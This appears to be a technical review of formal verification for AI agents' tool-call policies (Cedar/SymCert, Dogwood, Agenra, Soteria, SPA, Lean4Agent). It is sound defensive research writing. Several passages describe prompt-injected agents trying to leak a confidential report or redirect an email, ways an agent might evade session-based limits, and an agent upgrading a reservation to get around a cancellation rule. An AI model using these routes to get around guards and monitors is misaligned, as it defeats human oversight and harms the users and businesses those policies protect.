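An analysis is *sound* if no request can violate a property it reports as holding, and *complete* if every violation it reports is real. A sound but incomplete analysis misses no violations but can raise false alarms. According to *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026), Zelkova, an older AWS tool that handles about a billion queries a day about access to AWS resources, is sound but incomplete.

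SymCert is a Lean framework for building analyses of Cedar policies and proving them both sound and complete. The simplest one checks whether a set of policies C denies every request. In shortened form, its two theorems are:

```
result = "proved"          ⇒  for every r, C denies r
result = counterexample r  ⇒  C allows r
```

Here r stands for a request and the data about users and resources that Cedar consults. The theorems cover only well-formed r; for example, no group may contain itself. They also assume that the solver is correct. The 566 lines of Lean that connect SymCert to the solver have no proof either.

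### What SymCert proves and what it cost

Both theorems depend on showing that the translation into formulas preserves meaning. Let e be a condition, X a request with unknowns in it, and I an assignment of values to the unknowns. X[I] is the ordinary request that results from filling in the values. Torlak splits the claim into two properties:

```
compile(e, X)[I] = compile(e, X[I])     interpretability
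compile(e, x)    = evaluate(e, x)       reducibility, for x without unknowns
```

Interpretability means that one can translate first and fill in the values afterwards, or the other way round, with the same result. Reducibility means that when nothing is unknown, the translation simply computes the answer. Since X[I] has no unknowns, it can take the place of x, which gives

compile(e, X)[I] = compile(e, X[I]) = evaluate(e, X[I]).

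The condition "amount < 500", with an unknown amount n, translates to the formula n < 500. Setting n to 200 makes the formula true, and evaluating the condition on an actual $200 refund also gives true. This last step takes four lines in Lean, because the work is in proving the two properties. Torlak's earlier attempt to prove the whole claim at once in Dafny took about 8,000 lines for only part of Cedar, and the proof was hard to maintain.

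Completeness also requires repairing the solver's answer, because the solver can return a situation that could never occur. In Torlak's example of an online school, it returns a course category that contains itself. SymCert keeps the solver's answer for everything the policies can refer to and removes the group memberships of everything else. Torlak proves that the repaired situation is well-formed and that the policies treat it the same way as the original. The original design in *Cedar* (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024) had no method for turning the solver's answer into a real request, so it could not support a proof of completeness.

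The framework took 158 hours of programming and 505 hours of proof. Once it was built, Torlak programmed five analyses from an internal AWS service in under an hour and proved them sound and complete in another seven hours. Two of them check whether a set of policies allows everything or denies everything. The other three compare two sets, checking whether they are equivalent, whether they have no allowed request in common, and whether one allows every request the other allows. The shop can use the last analysis to check its refund limit. It writes a reference policy that permits only refunds under $500, then checks that this policy allows every refund the real policies allow.

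Torlak also ran a demonstration tool on eight example applications. The median query took at most 18 milliseconds to generate and 37 to solve, and no application took more than about seven seconds in total. In three of the eight, the tool found likely mistakes, such as redundant policies. When Cedar gained three new features, extending SymCert took a few minutes for one, four days for another and eight days for the third.

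The analysis service that AWS runs in production is also written in Rust, and the proved Lean version serves as the reference for daily random tests. The proofs connect the analysis to the Lean model of Cedar, but only testing connects that model to the Rust engine that decides live requests. *Introducing Cedar Analysis*, in which AWS presents an open-source version of the tools, therefore overstates what the proofs establish when it claims they ensure that the results exactly match how policies behave in production.

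### From English rules to Cedar policies

Administrators can write Cedar policies themselves or describe a rule in English and have a language model draft the policy. AgentCore generates a schema from the tools' descriptions, and the validator rejects drafts that refer to a tool or parameter that doesn't exist. The analysis then checks for policies that allow everything, allow nothing or contain impossible conditions, and its findings guide the next draft.

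One of AWS's examples requires a customer's tier to be both Gold and Platinum, where the author meant "or". Another permits a discount if the order quantity is at least 100 or less than 100, a condition that is always true. When an administrator attaches policies to a gateway, AgentCore also analyses them as a group, which can reveal that a permit for Gold customers' refunds under $100 never takes effect because a forbid blocks all their refunds under $500.

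Comparing the old and new versions of a policy can catch changes that do the opposite of what they seem to do. In an AWS example, a discount excludes limited-edition products, and someone adds a condition so that the exclusion applies only to orders of more than 200 items. The new policy allows a discount on 73 limited-edition items, which the old one denied, even though adding a condition looks stricter.

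These checks cannot show whether a policy matches what the administrator wanted. In an example from AWS's documentation page *Understanding Cedar policies*, the stated requirement is that refunds be $500 or less, but the policy requires an amount below 500, so Cedar would deny a refund of exactly $500. None of the checks would flag this policy, because it refers to real fields, allows some requests and denies others, and conflicts with nothing.

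That mistake errs on the side of caution, but others may not. Another AWS example translates "users with scope payment:process" into a check for whether the text "payment:process" appears anywhere in the user's list of permissions. If a company also had a permission called "payment:process-readonly", users with only that permission would pass the check and could transfer money.

A solver can find such errors only if somebody writes down the intended rule separately for comparison. AWS reports, without giving figures, that its checks make generated policies significantly more accurate, and it tells users to verify the result themselves. Testing a policy on real requests also helps. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026), an AWS service called Greenlight, in preview since December 2026, drafts policies from company documents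 and logs of tool calls. Before a team accepts a change, Greenlight shows which recorded calls the change would block. A log that included a $500 refund would have exposed the error in AWS's documentation.

### Why Cedar cannot limit an agent to one send

In the report task, a Cedar policy can require that the recipient be Alice if the administrator puts her address in it. The policy can also check the text of the email, but it has no record of whether that text came from Sanitize or from the raw report.

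It can't express the task's "at most once" rule at all. Cedar's decision depends only on three things:

decision = f(policies, request, data)

If the agent repeats an allowed request and the policies and data haven't changed, f returns the same answer, so an agent that is allowed to send Alice an email can send her the same one a thousand times.

The way around this is to add information to the request Cedar receives. AgentCore already adds the current time to each request, which lets the refund policy calculate an order's age. If it also added the number of emails sent so far, a policy could require that number to be zero. In August 2026, AWS introduced Dogwood, an open-source extension of Cedar that does something very similar. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026), Dogwood checks conditions about the past against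 a log of earlier calls and their results. It adds the answer to the request as an extra field, and Cedar still makes the decision.

AgentCore supports these conditions, so it supplies the missing memory. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* includes a policy that blocks a tool after three calls within five minutes. The same policy would work for the report task with a limit of one and a longer window, as long as it counts requests. A policy that counted successful responses would miss calls still in progress and failed attempts, which also count toward the task's limit. InfoQ relays AWS's example of three simultaneous $2,000 transfers under a $5,000 cap. None has finished when the gateway checks them, so the total of completed transfers is zero and all three go through.

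The count covers only one session and starts again at zero in the next. The calling program chooses the session's identifier, so AWS warns that such a limit is not a security control against a determined caller. A hijacked model that can only choose tool calls presumably can't change the identifier, but an agent that writes and runs its own code might be able to if that code can contact the gateway. AWS's *Temporal policies* also gives a maximum window of 24 hours for each condition, so an agent whose session stayed open longer could send a second email the next day.

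According to InfoQ, Cedar's automated reasoning tools don't support Dogwood's conditions about the past, and a set of policies that contains any of them can't be formally analysed. An administrator who adds "at most one send" can therefore no longer use the solver to check the policies over all possible requests.

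## Verified limits on a series of tool calls (Agenra)

The report task comes from Agenra, a policy language that, unlike Cedar, has built-in memory of earlier calls. Agenra's proofs cover that memory. Its permissions are *consumable authority*, meaning that each has a quota that every use reduces.

The model proposes a call, Python code passes the proposal to a compiled Lean core, and Python invokes the tool only if the core returns Allow. Some of the theorems by Shivakumar and colleagues are about companion models rather than the compiled functions themselves. *LEANGUARD* (2026) has a similar design, in which compiled Lean rules check each call against a journal of earlier events. Agenra differs by including a theorem about policy edits, which are riskier than they look.

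### The rules for the report task

Every value has a label ⟨s, C, t⟩. The sensitivity s is a level. In *AgentFlow* (2026), an earlier Python system by the same authors, the levels run from Public through Internal, Confidential and Restricted to TopSecret. C is a set of categories, such as Personal.Contact, and t is true if the value comes only from trusted sources. When an operation combines two values, the result gets the *join* of their labels:

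⟨s₁, C₁, t₁⟩ ⊔ ⟨s₂, C₂, t₂⟩ = ⟨max(s₁, s₂), C₁ ∪ C₂, t₁ ∧ t₂⟩

Suppose the report is labelled ⟨Confidential, {Finance}, true⟩ and the agent merges it with a web page labelled ⟨Public, ∅, false⟩. The result is labelled ⟨Confidential, {Finance}, false⟩, as secret as the report and as untrusted as the web page. The developer has declared that Sanitize lowers sensitivity, so its output is Public. Send accepts only public text. The labels follow declared dependencies between values, which gives a weaker guarantee than noninterference.

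A public label doesn't make a text the right one to send. A harmless notice from some other tool may also be public, and an attacker could have the agent send that to Alice instead of her summary. Agenra therefore has *argument-origin rules*, which say which operation must have produced an argument. Calls refer to earlier results by fixed names, or handles, so the core can trace each argument back. For the body of the email, the rule works like this:

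```
v has origin Sanitize if
  Sanitize produced v, or
  an origin-preserving operation produced v
    from a value that has origin Sanitize
```

A plain copy can preserve origin if the developer declares that it does, but a rewrite by a language model would normally lose it. The rule constrains Sanitize's output, but not its input unless the developer adds another rule.

The core keeps a *slot* for the recipient. The slot starts out unbound, and a successful result from the designated directory lookup fills it with an address. If the agent repeats the lookup and gets the same address, nothing changes. If it gets a different or malformed one, the slot becomes invalid for the rest of the task. Failed lookups have no effect. Send requires the recipient to match the slot, so an attacker who causes a conflicting second lookup can block the email but cannot redirect it, provided the directory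 itself can be trusted.

The quotas sit in two ledgers, one for what the user has granted and one for what the application permits. Every send needs a grant with quota left in both. The core charges both ledgers or neither, and it does so before Python contacts the mail server. Here is a complete run in simplified notation, with one send in each ledger:

```
r = Read()             r is Confidential
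c = Sanitize(r)        c is Public, with origin Sanitize
d = Lookup("Alice")
a = Extract(d)         the slot now holds Alice's address
Send(c, a)             both ledgers go from 1 to 0
```

An injected agent might try other calls, which fail for different reasons. In this table, n is a public notice from another tool and x is an address other than Alice's.

| Proposed call | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
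| Send(r, a) | reject | r is Confidential |
| Send(n, a) | reject | n does not come from Sanitize |
| Send(c, x) | reject | x does not match the slot |
| Send(c, a) before the lookup | reject | the slot is unbound |
| Send(c, a) | allow | every rule holds |
| Send(c, a) after a successful send | reject | no quota left |
| Send(c, a) after a mail server error | reject | the failed attempt kept its charge |

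The last row is the harshest because Alice may get no email at all, but allowing a retry can be worse. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (Xu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who approves one $500 transfer. The transfer succeeds, but the acknowledgement is lost and the agent asks again. A system that checks only whether the old approval token has been used may issue a new one and pay twice. In the paper's 10,152 runs with three families of models, agents frequently repeated an equivalent call when the outcome was uncertain.

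*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) makes the opposite choice. Its monitor reserves one use before the call and gives it back if the call verifiably did not execute. This saves Alice from losing a use to such a call, but it depends on good evidence of failure, which a timeout doesn't provide. Xu and colleagues use a better approach where the service supports it. Every retry carries the same identifying key, and the service returns the earlier result instead of acting again. Agenra's proofs don't cover what a remote service does with a repeated request.

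A developer can also require a person's approval for a specific call. The approval is valid once, for the same operation with the same handles and arguments in the same order, and the core uses it up before the call goes out. The call must still pass the other rules, so the label check blocks the raw report even if a reviewer approves everything.

The enforcement theorem is that every call in the core's record passed every applicable check in the state in which the core admitted it, that both ledgers covered every effect, and that no finite quota was exceeded. A later event, such as a conflicting lookup, does not undo an earlier decision.

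### Searching for mistakes in the policy

The enforcement theorem holds even if the policy itself is a mistake, such as one with a send quota of two. To find mistakes in a policy, Agenra searches all sequences of events up to a given length, using the same Lean transitions that it uses for live decisions. Shivakumar and colleagues prove that the search is sound and complete up to that length, for the outcomes that the developer has declared possible.

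The search also detects when a policy is *vacuous*, meaning that it allows no delivery within the bound. With approvals included, the report policy is vacuous at five events, presumably because the approval adds an event to the five operations. At six and at eight events, it is useful and free of violations. When Shivakumar and colleagues raised only the send quota to two, the search found a run with two sends, each with a sanitized body and its own fresh approval. The run also worked on real storage. Removing the origin rule, widening the recipient or dropping the approval also produced a violation.

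This only works for small workflows. At six events the search visited 66,575 nodes and took 0.8 seconds, while at eight it visited 12.3 million and took 154 seconds.

### What the trials with live agents add

Shivakumar and colleagues ran two language models, Qwen and Hermes, on the delivery task with no guard, with a guard they wrote by hand, and with Agenra. Without attacks, each model delivered the report in all five runs of every condition. Under attack and without a guard, Qwen sent the raw report in 15 of 20 runs and Hermes in 1 of 20. With either guard, neither model sent it. Under attack, Qwen completed the task in 5 of 20 runs and Hermes in 10 of 20, with or without a guard.

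These runs used an earlier policy without the origin rule, and their results showed that the rule was needed. When Shivakumar and colleagues replayed the recorded calls, they found five with an improper body that the policy allowed but the handwritten guard blocked. With the origin rule, Agenra rejects all five and still accepts all six legitimate orders of work, which are the ways to interleave Read and Sanitize with Lookup and Extract before sending.

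In further trials with Claude Sonnet 5.5 and Haiku 5.5, the attacks on GitHub tasks never succeeded even without a guard, so those trials couldn't show a benefit from the guard. A much larger test of AgentFlow used 949 cases from AgentDojo, a standard prompt-injection benchmark. Confirmed attacks fell from 33.0% to zero, and task completion rose from 46.7% to 63.3%. But AgentFlow's engine is ordinary Python, so these results are evidence for this kind of policy and not for Agenra's Lean core.

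One advantage of Agenra over a handwritten guard that stops the same attacks is that it moves bookkeeping from code into declarations, and software can compare two versions of a declaration much more easily than two versions of a program. Shivakumar and colleagues also implemented the report task on the policy engine of CaMeL, an earlier defence that attaches information about sources and permitted readers to each value. The two versions agreed on all 416 test cases. The Agenra version was longer, with 79 lines of code and 37 of declarations against 70 lines for the CaMeL version, but it had 3 branches instead of 13 and 1 changeable field instead of 9.

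### Deleting A and B

Suppose a user lets an agent delete file A once and file B once. The ledger lists two grants in this order:

```
g₁: delete A       quota 1
g₂: delete B       quota 1
```

Agenra charges each deletion to the first grant in the list that covers it and still has quota, a method known as *first-fit*. The agent can delete the files in either order. It can't delete a third file C, and it can't delete the same file twice, even if somebody has put a new file in its place.

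Now an administrator widens g₁ to cover both A and B.

| Sequence | Old policy | New policy |
|---|---|---|
| A, then B | g₁, then g₂ | g₁, then g₂ |
| B, then A | g₂, then g₁ | g₁, then A is refused |
| B, then B | g₂, then B is refused | g₁, then g₂ |

In the second row, the new policy charges B to g₁, because g₁ comes first and now covers it. Since g₂ covers only B, nothing is left for A, and an agent that has always deleted B first can no longer go on to delete A. In the third row, the same change allows a double deletion that the old policy stopped.

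Comparing the old and new policies on single requests would miss both problems, because on a fresh ledger both policies accept "delete A" and "delete B" and refuse "delete C".

The two failures need separate checks. A revision is *safe* if the new policy allows nothing forbidden, and it *preserves workflows* if the new policy accepts every sequence the old one accepted. In the report task, raising the send quota from one to two preserves every workflow but is unsafe, while lowering it to zero is safe but blocks every delivery.

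Charging B to g₂, the narrower grant, would have avoided the problem in this example, but no replacement for first-fit works in general. In *Managing Digital Rights using Linear Logic*, Barth and Mitchell (2006) studied the same problem in licences for digital music. They showed that any algorithm that decides which right to use up as each action occurs will sometimes refuse an action under one licence that it would allow under a less flexible one.

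Suppose, for example, that a licence has two single-use rights, one for song X or Y and the other for song X or Z. When the listener plays X, the player has to use up one of them. If it uses the first, Y is no longer available. But under a narrower licence whose first right covered only Y, the player would have to use the second right for X, and Y would still be available. The same problem arises with Z if the player uses the second right for X.

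Barth and Mitchell offer two remedies. One is to restrict licences to a class in which the problem can't arise. The other is to let the player revise its past decisions, so that when the listener asks for Y, it can move the charge for X to the other right. Agenra instead keeps first-fit and tries to prove for each edit that it harms no workflow.

### The simulation between old and new ledgers

Let L be a state of the old ledger and M a state of the new one. Write L —e→ L′ if the ledger in state L accepts the effect e, charges a grant and moves to state L′. A relation R between old and new states is a *simulation* if it meets two conditions:

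1. R(L₀, M₀) holds for the initial states.
2. If R(L, M) and L —e→ L′, then M —e→ M′ for some M′ with R(L′, M′).

By induction, the new ledger accepts every sequence that the old one accepts. Every step under the old policy must have a counterpart under the new one, so the new policy allows at least as much as the old one. Moon and Varshney's refinement for PocketFlow works in the opposite direction, showing that the concrete system can't do more than the abstract one.

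For a quota increase, let R(L, M) mean that every grant has at least as much quota left in the new ledger M as in the old ledger L. R holds at the start. Suppose the old ledger charges e to grant i. Grant i then also has quota left in the new ledger, so the new ledger accepts e and charges it either to i or to an earlier grant j. If it charges i, then i loses one unit in both ledgers and R still holds. If it charges j, then j must be empty in the old ledger, because first-fit would otherwise have used it there. After the charge, j has at least zero units left in the new ledger, and i has lost a unit only in the old one, so R still holds.

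Adding a grant at the end of the list is the same case, since the new grant can be treated as one that was always there with a quota of zero. Reordering works for *independent* grants, meaning grants that never cover the same effect. Swapping two neighbouring independent grants doesn't change which grant is the first to cover a given deletion, so the two ledgers always charge the same grant, and R can simply require that they have the same quotas left. Overlapping grants must keep their relative order.

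No simulation exists for the widening of g₁. After the agent deletes B, the remaining quotas of g₁ and g₂ are (1, 0) in the old ledger and (0, 1) in the new one. Condition 2 would require R to relate these two states, but the old ledger then accepts the deletion of A and the new one refuses it.

Agenra's actual proof covers more than this sketch. A single call can have several effects, such as deleting both files, and the core must count all of them toward the limits or none. The relation also covers typed arguments, address slots that fill up during the run, and failed calls.

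### The test on 51 revisions

Agenra has two ways to certify that a revision preserves workflows. A structural certificate covers edits like the ones just described. For other edits to ledgers with finite quotas, the software can propose an explicit list of paired states, and Lean checks that the list is closed under every step. For example, such a list can certify an edit that widens g₂, instead of g₁, to cover both files. Pairing each of the four old states with the identical new state gives a simulation, because deletions of A still go to g₁ first. This revision preserves every workflow but now allows A to be deleted twice, so it would fail a safety check.

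Shivakumar and colleagues wrote 51 revisions to test this. Agenra certified all 21 revisions that preserved every workflow, 16 with structural certificates and 5 with explicit simulations. It certified none of the 30 that broke at least one workflow.

The finding that Agenra certified none of the 30 harmful revisions deserves more confidence than its success on all 21 harmless ones. Given the theorem, Agenra should never certify a harmful revision as long as the assumptions hold, so the first result mainly tests the code around the proof. No theorem guarantees the second result, because the conditions are sufficient but not necessary, and Shivakumar and colleagues acknowledge that Agenra will fail to certify some harmless edits. How often that happens in practice depends on what edits people make, which can't be learned from revisions written by the checker's designers.

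Agenra has certified at least one real quota change, in which Dyad, a tool for building apps with AI, doubled its free allowance from five messages to 10 (*Basic Agent free quota increased to 10 messages*). Dyad's *More free Basic Agent messages, build verification in Agent mode* reports a later increase to 20 a day. So people do revise such quotas, but a plain increase is the easiest kind of edit to certify. Changes to overlapping permissions, which caused the trouble with A and B, would be a harder test, and nobody has yet collected examples from deployed agents.

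The certificates are also limited by the number of cases Agenra must check. To cover every state of the address slots, it enumerates d(r + 1)ˢ cases for d sample requests, r possible resources and s slots, since each slot may be unbound or hold any one of the resources. One configuration with five slots needed 472,392 cases, more than the cap of 200,000. When no certificate applies, Agenra uses the bounded search instead.

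### What the preservation theorem assumes

The theorem compares two runs, one under each policy, that start in the same state and receive the same requests. Calls must be *serialized*, meaning each one finishes before the next begins. If an agent starts a second deletion while the first is still pending, the theorem does not apply. It also does not cover mid-task resets or anything that happens after a refusal.

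The theorem assumes that outside services return the same results in both runs. If the directory lookup succeeds under the old policy but times out under the new one, the address slot stays empty and Send fails, even though the new policy is no stricter. The theorem therefore guarantees only that the edit won't be what keeps Alice from getting her summary. She may still not get it if the directory is down.

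The developer's declared requests must include every request the tools actually make, and the declared labels and dependencies must be correct. If a tool deletes a file and also makes an undeclared deletion of its backup, neither ledger records the backup's deletion.

Finally, the theorem relies on the Python layer around the Lean core. Separate certificates check some of the policy translations, but the rest have no proof. Python also matches its own objects to the core's handles and invokes the tools, and a mistake in invoking them could make all the other checks ineffective. Agent frameworks often run checks as callbacks, and some might log a callback's error and continue. If a framework did that with Agenra's rejection, Python would send the second email even though the core had correctly refused it.

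## Plans checked before the agent acts (Soteria and Lean4Agent)

Agenra checks each call as it arrives, which Meijer considers too late to prevent some mistakes. If an airline's agent refunds a ticket and a monitor then blocks the forbidden cancellation, the customer has both the money and the seat. A checker that examines the whole plan first can reject it before the agent issues the refund.

*SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) presents such a checker for plans made of tool calls. *Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) checks workflows made of instructions to a language model. Both represent the agent's work as a graph and attach conditions to its steps, but Lean4Agent assumes far more about the model.

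### Contracts for single steps

A *contract* gives a tool t the same two conditions that Dafny programmers give a piece of code, a precondition P for the call and a postcondition Q for the result:

{P} t {Q}

For a payment tool, P might require a positive amount and a valid payment method, and Q might require that the tool return a confirmation number.

*ToolGate* (Liu, Peng and colleagues, 2026) checks such contracts one call at a time. It keeps a table of trusted facts and lets the model choose only among tools whose preconditions hold in that table. After a call, it adds the result to the table if the postcondition holds and discards the result otherwise. Discarding a result doesn't undo the call, so a payment with a malformed confirmation number may still have gone out. Checking one call at a time also can't show in advance that the agent will be able to finish. The agent may get halfway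 through a task and find that no useful tool's preconditions hold.

### A cancellation plan that breaks a rule

Soteria uses contracts for single calls and adds *policy specifications*, which are logical formulas about the whole trace. One airline rule requires the agent to check that the customer hasn't already flown before it cancels a reservation. In words close to the formula:

```
for every call c to Cancel
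  there is an earlier call d to NoFlown with
    d.reservation = c.reservation  and  d.result = true
```

The model writes its plan as a *guarded transition system*, a graph whose nodes are states and whose edges are transitions. Each transition makes at most one call and leads to another state. It can fire only if its *guard*, a condition on the data collected so far, is true. Here is a faulty plan from the paper, in simplified notation, for an airline that allows cancellation within 24 hours of booking:

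```
LOOKUP:       resv := GetReservation(id)            → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hours := HoursSince(resv.created)     → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if hours <= 24                        → DO_CANCEL
              otherwise                             → NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL:    Cancel(id, reason)                    → DONE
```

The plan ends in either DONE or NOT_PERMITTED. A passenger who booked in the morning and flew at noon could cancel the ticket that evening, even though the plan looks sensible.

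Soteria translates the plan into Dafny and adds *ghost state*, which is data that exists only for the proof. The ghost state includes a step counter and a log of the calls to each tool that the rules mention. At each final state, Dafny must prove that the logs satisfy every rule. This plan has two paths:

| Path after CHECK_RULES | Cancel log | NoFlown log | Rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| NOT_PERMITTED | empty | empty | holds |
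| DO_CANCEL, DONE | one call | empty | fails |

The first path satisfies the rule because it cancels nothing. The second path fails because the rule requires an earlier entry in the NoFlown log, and there is none. Dafny reports the failure, and Soteria sends the model a message naming the broken rule. In the main experiments, the model could retry up to eight times.

The repair adds a state after the lookup:

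```
LOOKUP:       resv := GetReservation(id)            → CHECK_FLOWN
CHECK_FLOWN:  ok := NoFlown(id)                     → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hours := HoursSince(resv.created)     → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if ok and hours <= 24                 → DO_CANCEL
              otherwise                             → NOT_PERMITTED
```

The plan must both call NoFlown and test `ok` before cancelling. The rule requires NoFlown to return "true", but Dafny relies only on a tool's postcondition to determine what it can return, and NoFlown's also allows "false". Without the test, verification would fail because the plan could cancel after NoFlown returns "false".

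### What else the verifier proves

Dafny also checks the contracts and makes sure the plan can't get stuck. For each state s, it works out a formula Σ(s) that describes everything the plan knows on arrival there. If a transition with guard g calls tool a with arguments v, and P is the tool's precondition, Dafny must prove

Σ(s) ∧ g ⇒ P(v).

For a state with guards g₁ to gₙ, it must also prove

Σ(s) ⇒ g₁ ∨ … ∨ gₙ,

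which means that at least one transition can always fire. If the plan tested for "hours < 24" and "hours > 24", this check would fail, because a booking made exactly 24 hours ago would satisfy neither guard.

Checking a whole plan can enforce some rules about what the agent must do later. One of Soteria's rules for file tasks requires the agent to read a file back after writing it. A monitor can't enforce this by blocking calls, because the write is acceptable when it happens and the violation is the agent's failure to read the file afterward. Soteria's plans have no cycles, so every path ends, and Dafny can check at the end of each one whether the read took place. A real run might still crash between the write and the read.

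A third kind of rule concerns where a value came from. He and colleagues give the example that a refund amount must derive from a lookup of the same reservation. The verifier records which tools contributed to each variable, but it doesn't distinguish between calls to the same tool. Suppose a plan looks up a $100 reservation and a $900 one, then refunds $900 for the first. The plan would pass the check as described, because the amount came from the lookup tool and the plan looked up the first reservation. The experiments don't use this example rule.

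Long plans are hard for a model to get right, so Soteria has a library of verified *sub-plans* for standard procedures such as cancellation. A larger plan can call a sub-plan like a tool, and the verifier then uses only the sub-plan's contract. With sub-plans, GPT-5.4-mini produced a plan that passed every check in 65 of 68 planning attempts, compared with 38 of 60 without them.

### When the agent departs from the plan

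By default, the agent doesn't have to follow the verified plan. Soteria shows the model the remaining steps as a *worklist* and prunes branches as results arrive. For example, if a booking turns out to be 26 hours old, Soteria removes the branch for recent bookings. The model still chooses each call, and a runtime monitor checks the call against the contracts and rules.

Suppose the model skips a step and tries to cancel immediately after the lookup. The monitor adds the proposed call to the trace, finds no earlier NoFlown call, blocks the cancellation and reports the missing call. The model calls NoFlown, which returns "true", and tries again. This time the monitor allows the cancellation.

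Soteria also has a strict mode, in which the agent can make only the calls that the plan permits in its current state. If a customer asks to cancel one reservation and look up another, strict mode blocks the lookup of the other reservation unless the plan includes it. The default mode allows it because a lookup breaks no rule.

In the default mode, the monitor enforces the rules and the verified plan serves mainly as guidance. If the model uses up its retries, Soteria runs a partly verified plan, with warnings about the rules Dafny couldn't prove. The monitor's code hasn't been formally verified. In the strict mode, Soteria runs only fully verified plans and doesn't use the monitor to check the rules.

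### How much Soteria helped

He and colleagues tested Soteria on 50 airline tasks and 114 retail tasks from τ²-bench, in which a language model plays the customer, and on 43 tasks from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long tasks involving files and documents. They compared it with four baselines. One put the policy in the model's prompt but did not enforce it. NeMo Guardrails had a language model judge each call, while AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts checked calls against formal rules at runtime.

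A task counts as a success if the agent completes it without breaking any rule. This table gives Soteria's success rates in percent, with the best baseline for each case in brackets:

| Model | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 60.0 (50.0) | 35.1 (20.2) | 11.6 (2.3) |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 62.0 (36.0) | 45.6 (38.6) | 16.3 (2.3) |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.0 (30.0) | 56.1 (31.6) | 9.3 (4.7) |
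| Claude Opus 4.6 | 88.0 (56.0) | 90.4 (46.5) | 18.6 (11.6) |

Soteria's success rate was, on average, 1.7 times that of the best baseline. Its agents never broke a rule, while every baseline broke at least one with every model on every benchmark.

The monitor blocks violations of the same 98 rules that the evaluation counts, so the absence of violations is less impressive than it sounds. He and colleagues also corrected some rules and added missing ones while auditing the results.

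The rules may still miss some policy violations. In one airline task, GPT-5.4-mini without a guard upgraded a reservation to business class to make it eligible for cancellation, then cancelled it. The benchmark gave full credit, although He and colleagues consider the upgrade a workaround that the policy doesn't permit. None of their 24 airline rules forbids it. If the agent looked up the reservation again after the upgrade, it would find a business-class booking, which the rules allow it to cancel as long as the customer hasn't flown.

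Plans also raised the success rate. Unguarded Opus often collected all the information for a retail task and then transferred the customer to a human. It made the required change in only 57% of the tasks that needed one, compared with all of them when it had a plan that specified which change to make and when.

It is unclear how much of this came from verifying the plans. On the airline tasks, adding verification to an unverified plan raised GPT-5.4-mini's success rate from 44% to 46% (one task in 50) and left Gemini's at 32%. Adding sub-plans then raised the two models' rates by 4 and 6 points, respectively, and adding the monitor raised them by another 10 and 24. He and colleagues didn't test the monitor with an unverified plan, which would have shown whether verification still matters once a monitor is in place.

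Most of the results come from single runs. When He and colleagues ran the airline tasks five times with GPT-5.4-mini and only three retries, Soteria averaged 50.8% and AgentSpec 48.0%, with overlapping confidence intervals. If rule violations are ignored, Haiku and Opus completed fewer Toolathlon tasks with Soteria than without any guard (9.3% against 16.3% for Haiku, and 18.6% against 30.2% for Opus). Soteria also cost about two to seven times as much as the unguarded agent on the airline and retail tasks, because it writes a new plan each time the customer replies. On Toolathlon, which needs only one plan per task, it was cheaper.

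### What a fixed plan gives up

If the model writes a plan before the agent has seen any data, the plan can branch on a result only if the model anticipated that the result would matter. Predicting which results will matter is easy for cancellations, where the airline's policy lists the relevant facts, but much harder for debugging, where the error message from one command determines what to try next.

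In Soteria, guards handle the expected variations, and the default mode lets the model make calls that aren't in the plan. When the customer says something new, Soteria writes another plan. A plan can also include an `llm_eval` step, which asks a language model to make a judgement during the run, such as choosing a suitable flight from a list.

*SPA* takes a stricter approach. Its planner runs once per request, before any tool, and never sees the results. If the plan fails a check or a tool returns an error, the request ends. In return, SPA's language is simple enough for a short program to check every plan completely. A plan consists of steps that retrieve stored data, call a tool, query an isolated language model, show something to the user, branch or loop. The designers left out several constructs that programmers normally rely on:

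| Left out | What a plan can do instead |
|---|---|
| arithmetic and text templates | pass the values to a tool or the isolated model |
| "and" and "or" in conditions | nest one condition inside another |
| open-ended loops | go through a collection once, item by item |
| user-defined functions | write the steps out again |

If the airline also let business-class passengers cancel at any time, a Soteria guard could read "hours <= 24 or cabin = business". In SPA, the plan has to repeat the cancellation step:

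```
condition hours <= 24
  then  Cancel(id)
  else  condition cabin = "business"
          then  Cancel(id)
          else  display "not permitted"
```

In a general-purpose language, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it will reach a particular call. SPA avoids this problem because its loops always end and the text of a plan shows which values each step depends on. The checker goes through the plan once, tracking how secret and how trustworthy each value is. One check of a loop's body is enough, however many items the loop covers, because variables created in the body disappear at the end of each pass.

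Soteria also rejects plans with cycles, but it keeps arithmetic and compound conditions, which make its plans more expressive. However, Dafny may fail to find a proof for a correct plan. He et al. gave Dafny ten seconds per state.

SPA's strictness reduces the number of tasks the agent completes. On AgentDojo without attacks, GPT-5.4-nano, a small model, completed 53.0% of tasks with the secrecy and trust check off and 29.0% with it on. The check rejected about half the plans, typically because they passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data. SPA doesn't allow retries, so that the planner can't keep revising an unsafe plan until the checker accepts it. This precaution matters only if the checker or its policy has a gap. If neither does, the checker will reject every unsafe revision, and retries like Soteria's would recover some of the lost tasks without reducing safety.

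### The three layers of Lean4Agent

Lean4Agent instead checks workflows made up mostly of English instructions to a language model, such as "reproduce the bug" or "verify the fix". Lean checks in three layers whether the steps fit together. A proof about the workflow doesn't limit which commands the agent runs, because the model can call tools freely within a step, up to 20 times in the printed examples.

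The first layer covers the structure of the graph, including whether every step is reachable and every variable has a value before a step reads it. In one faulty workflow, four searches run in parallel and a later step is meant to merge their results. No step collects the results from the parallel branches first, so the merging step would refer to variables that don't exist.

The second layer gives each step a contract. In another faulty workflow, one step finds evidence in a paper and the next uses it to write an answer:

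```
find_evidence    promises   evidence with field: snippets
compose_answer   requires   evidence with fields: passages, summary
```

Both steps refer to the same variable, so the first layer finds no problem. Lean rejects the workflow because no earlier step guarantees the fields that `compose_answer` needs. This layer also tracks information in the conversation. Some steps receive the earlier conversation, while others start without it and can use information from it only if the workflow passes that information in a variable.

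A language model writes the contracts from the instructions. Wang and colleagues checked all 1,460 conditions in the 12 workflows they tested and found 36 errors, none of which changed whether a workflow passed.

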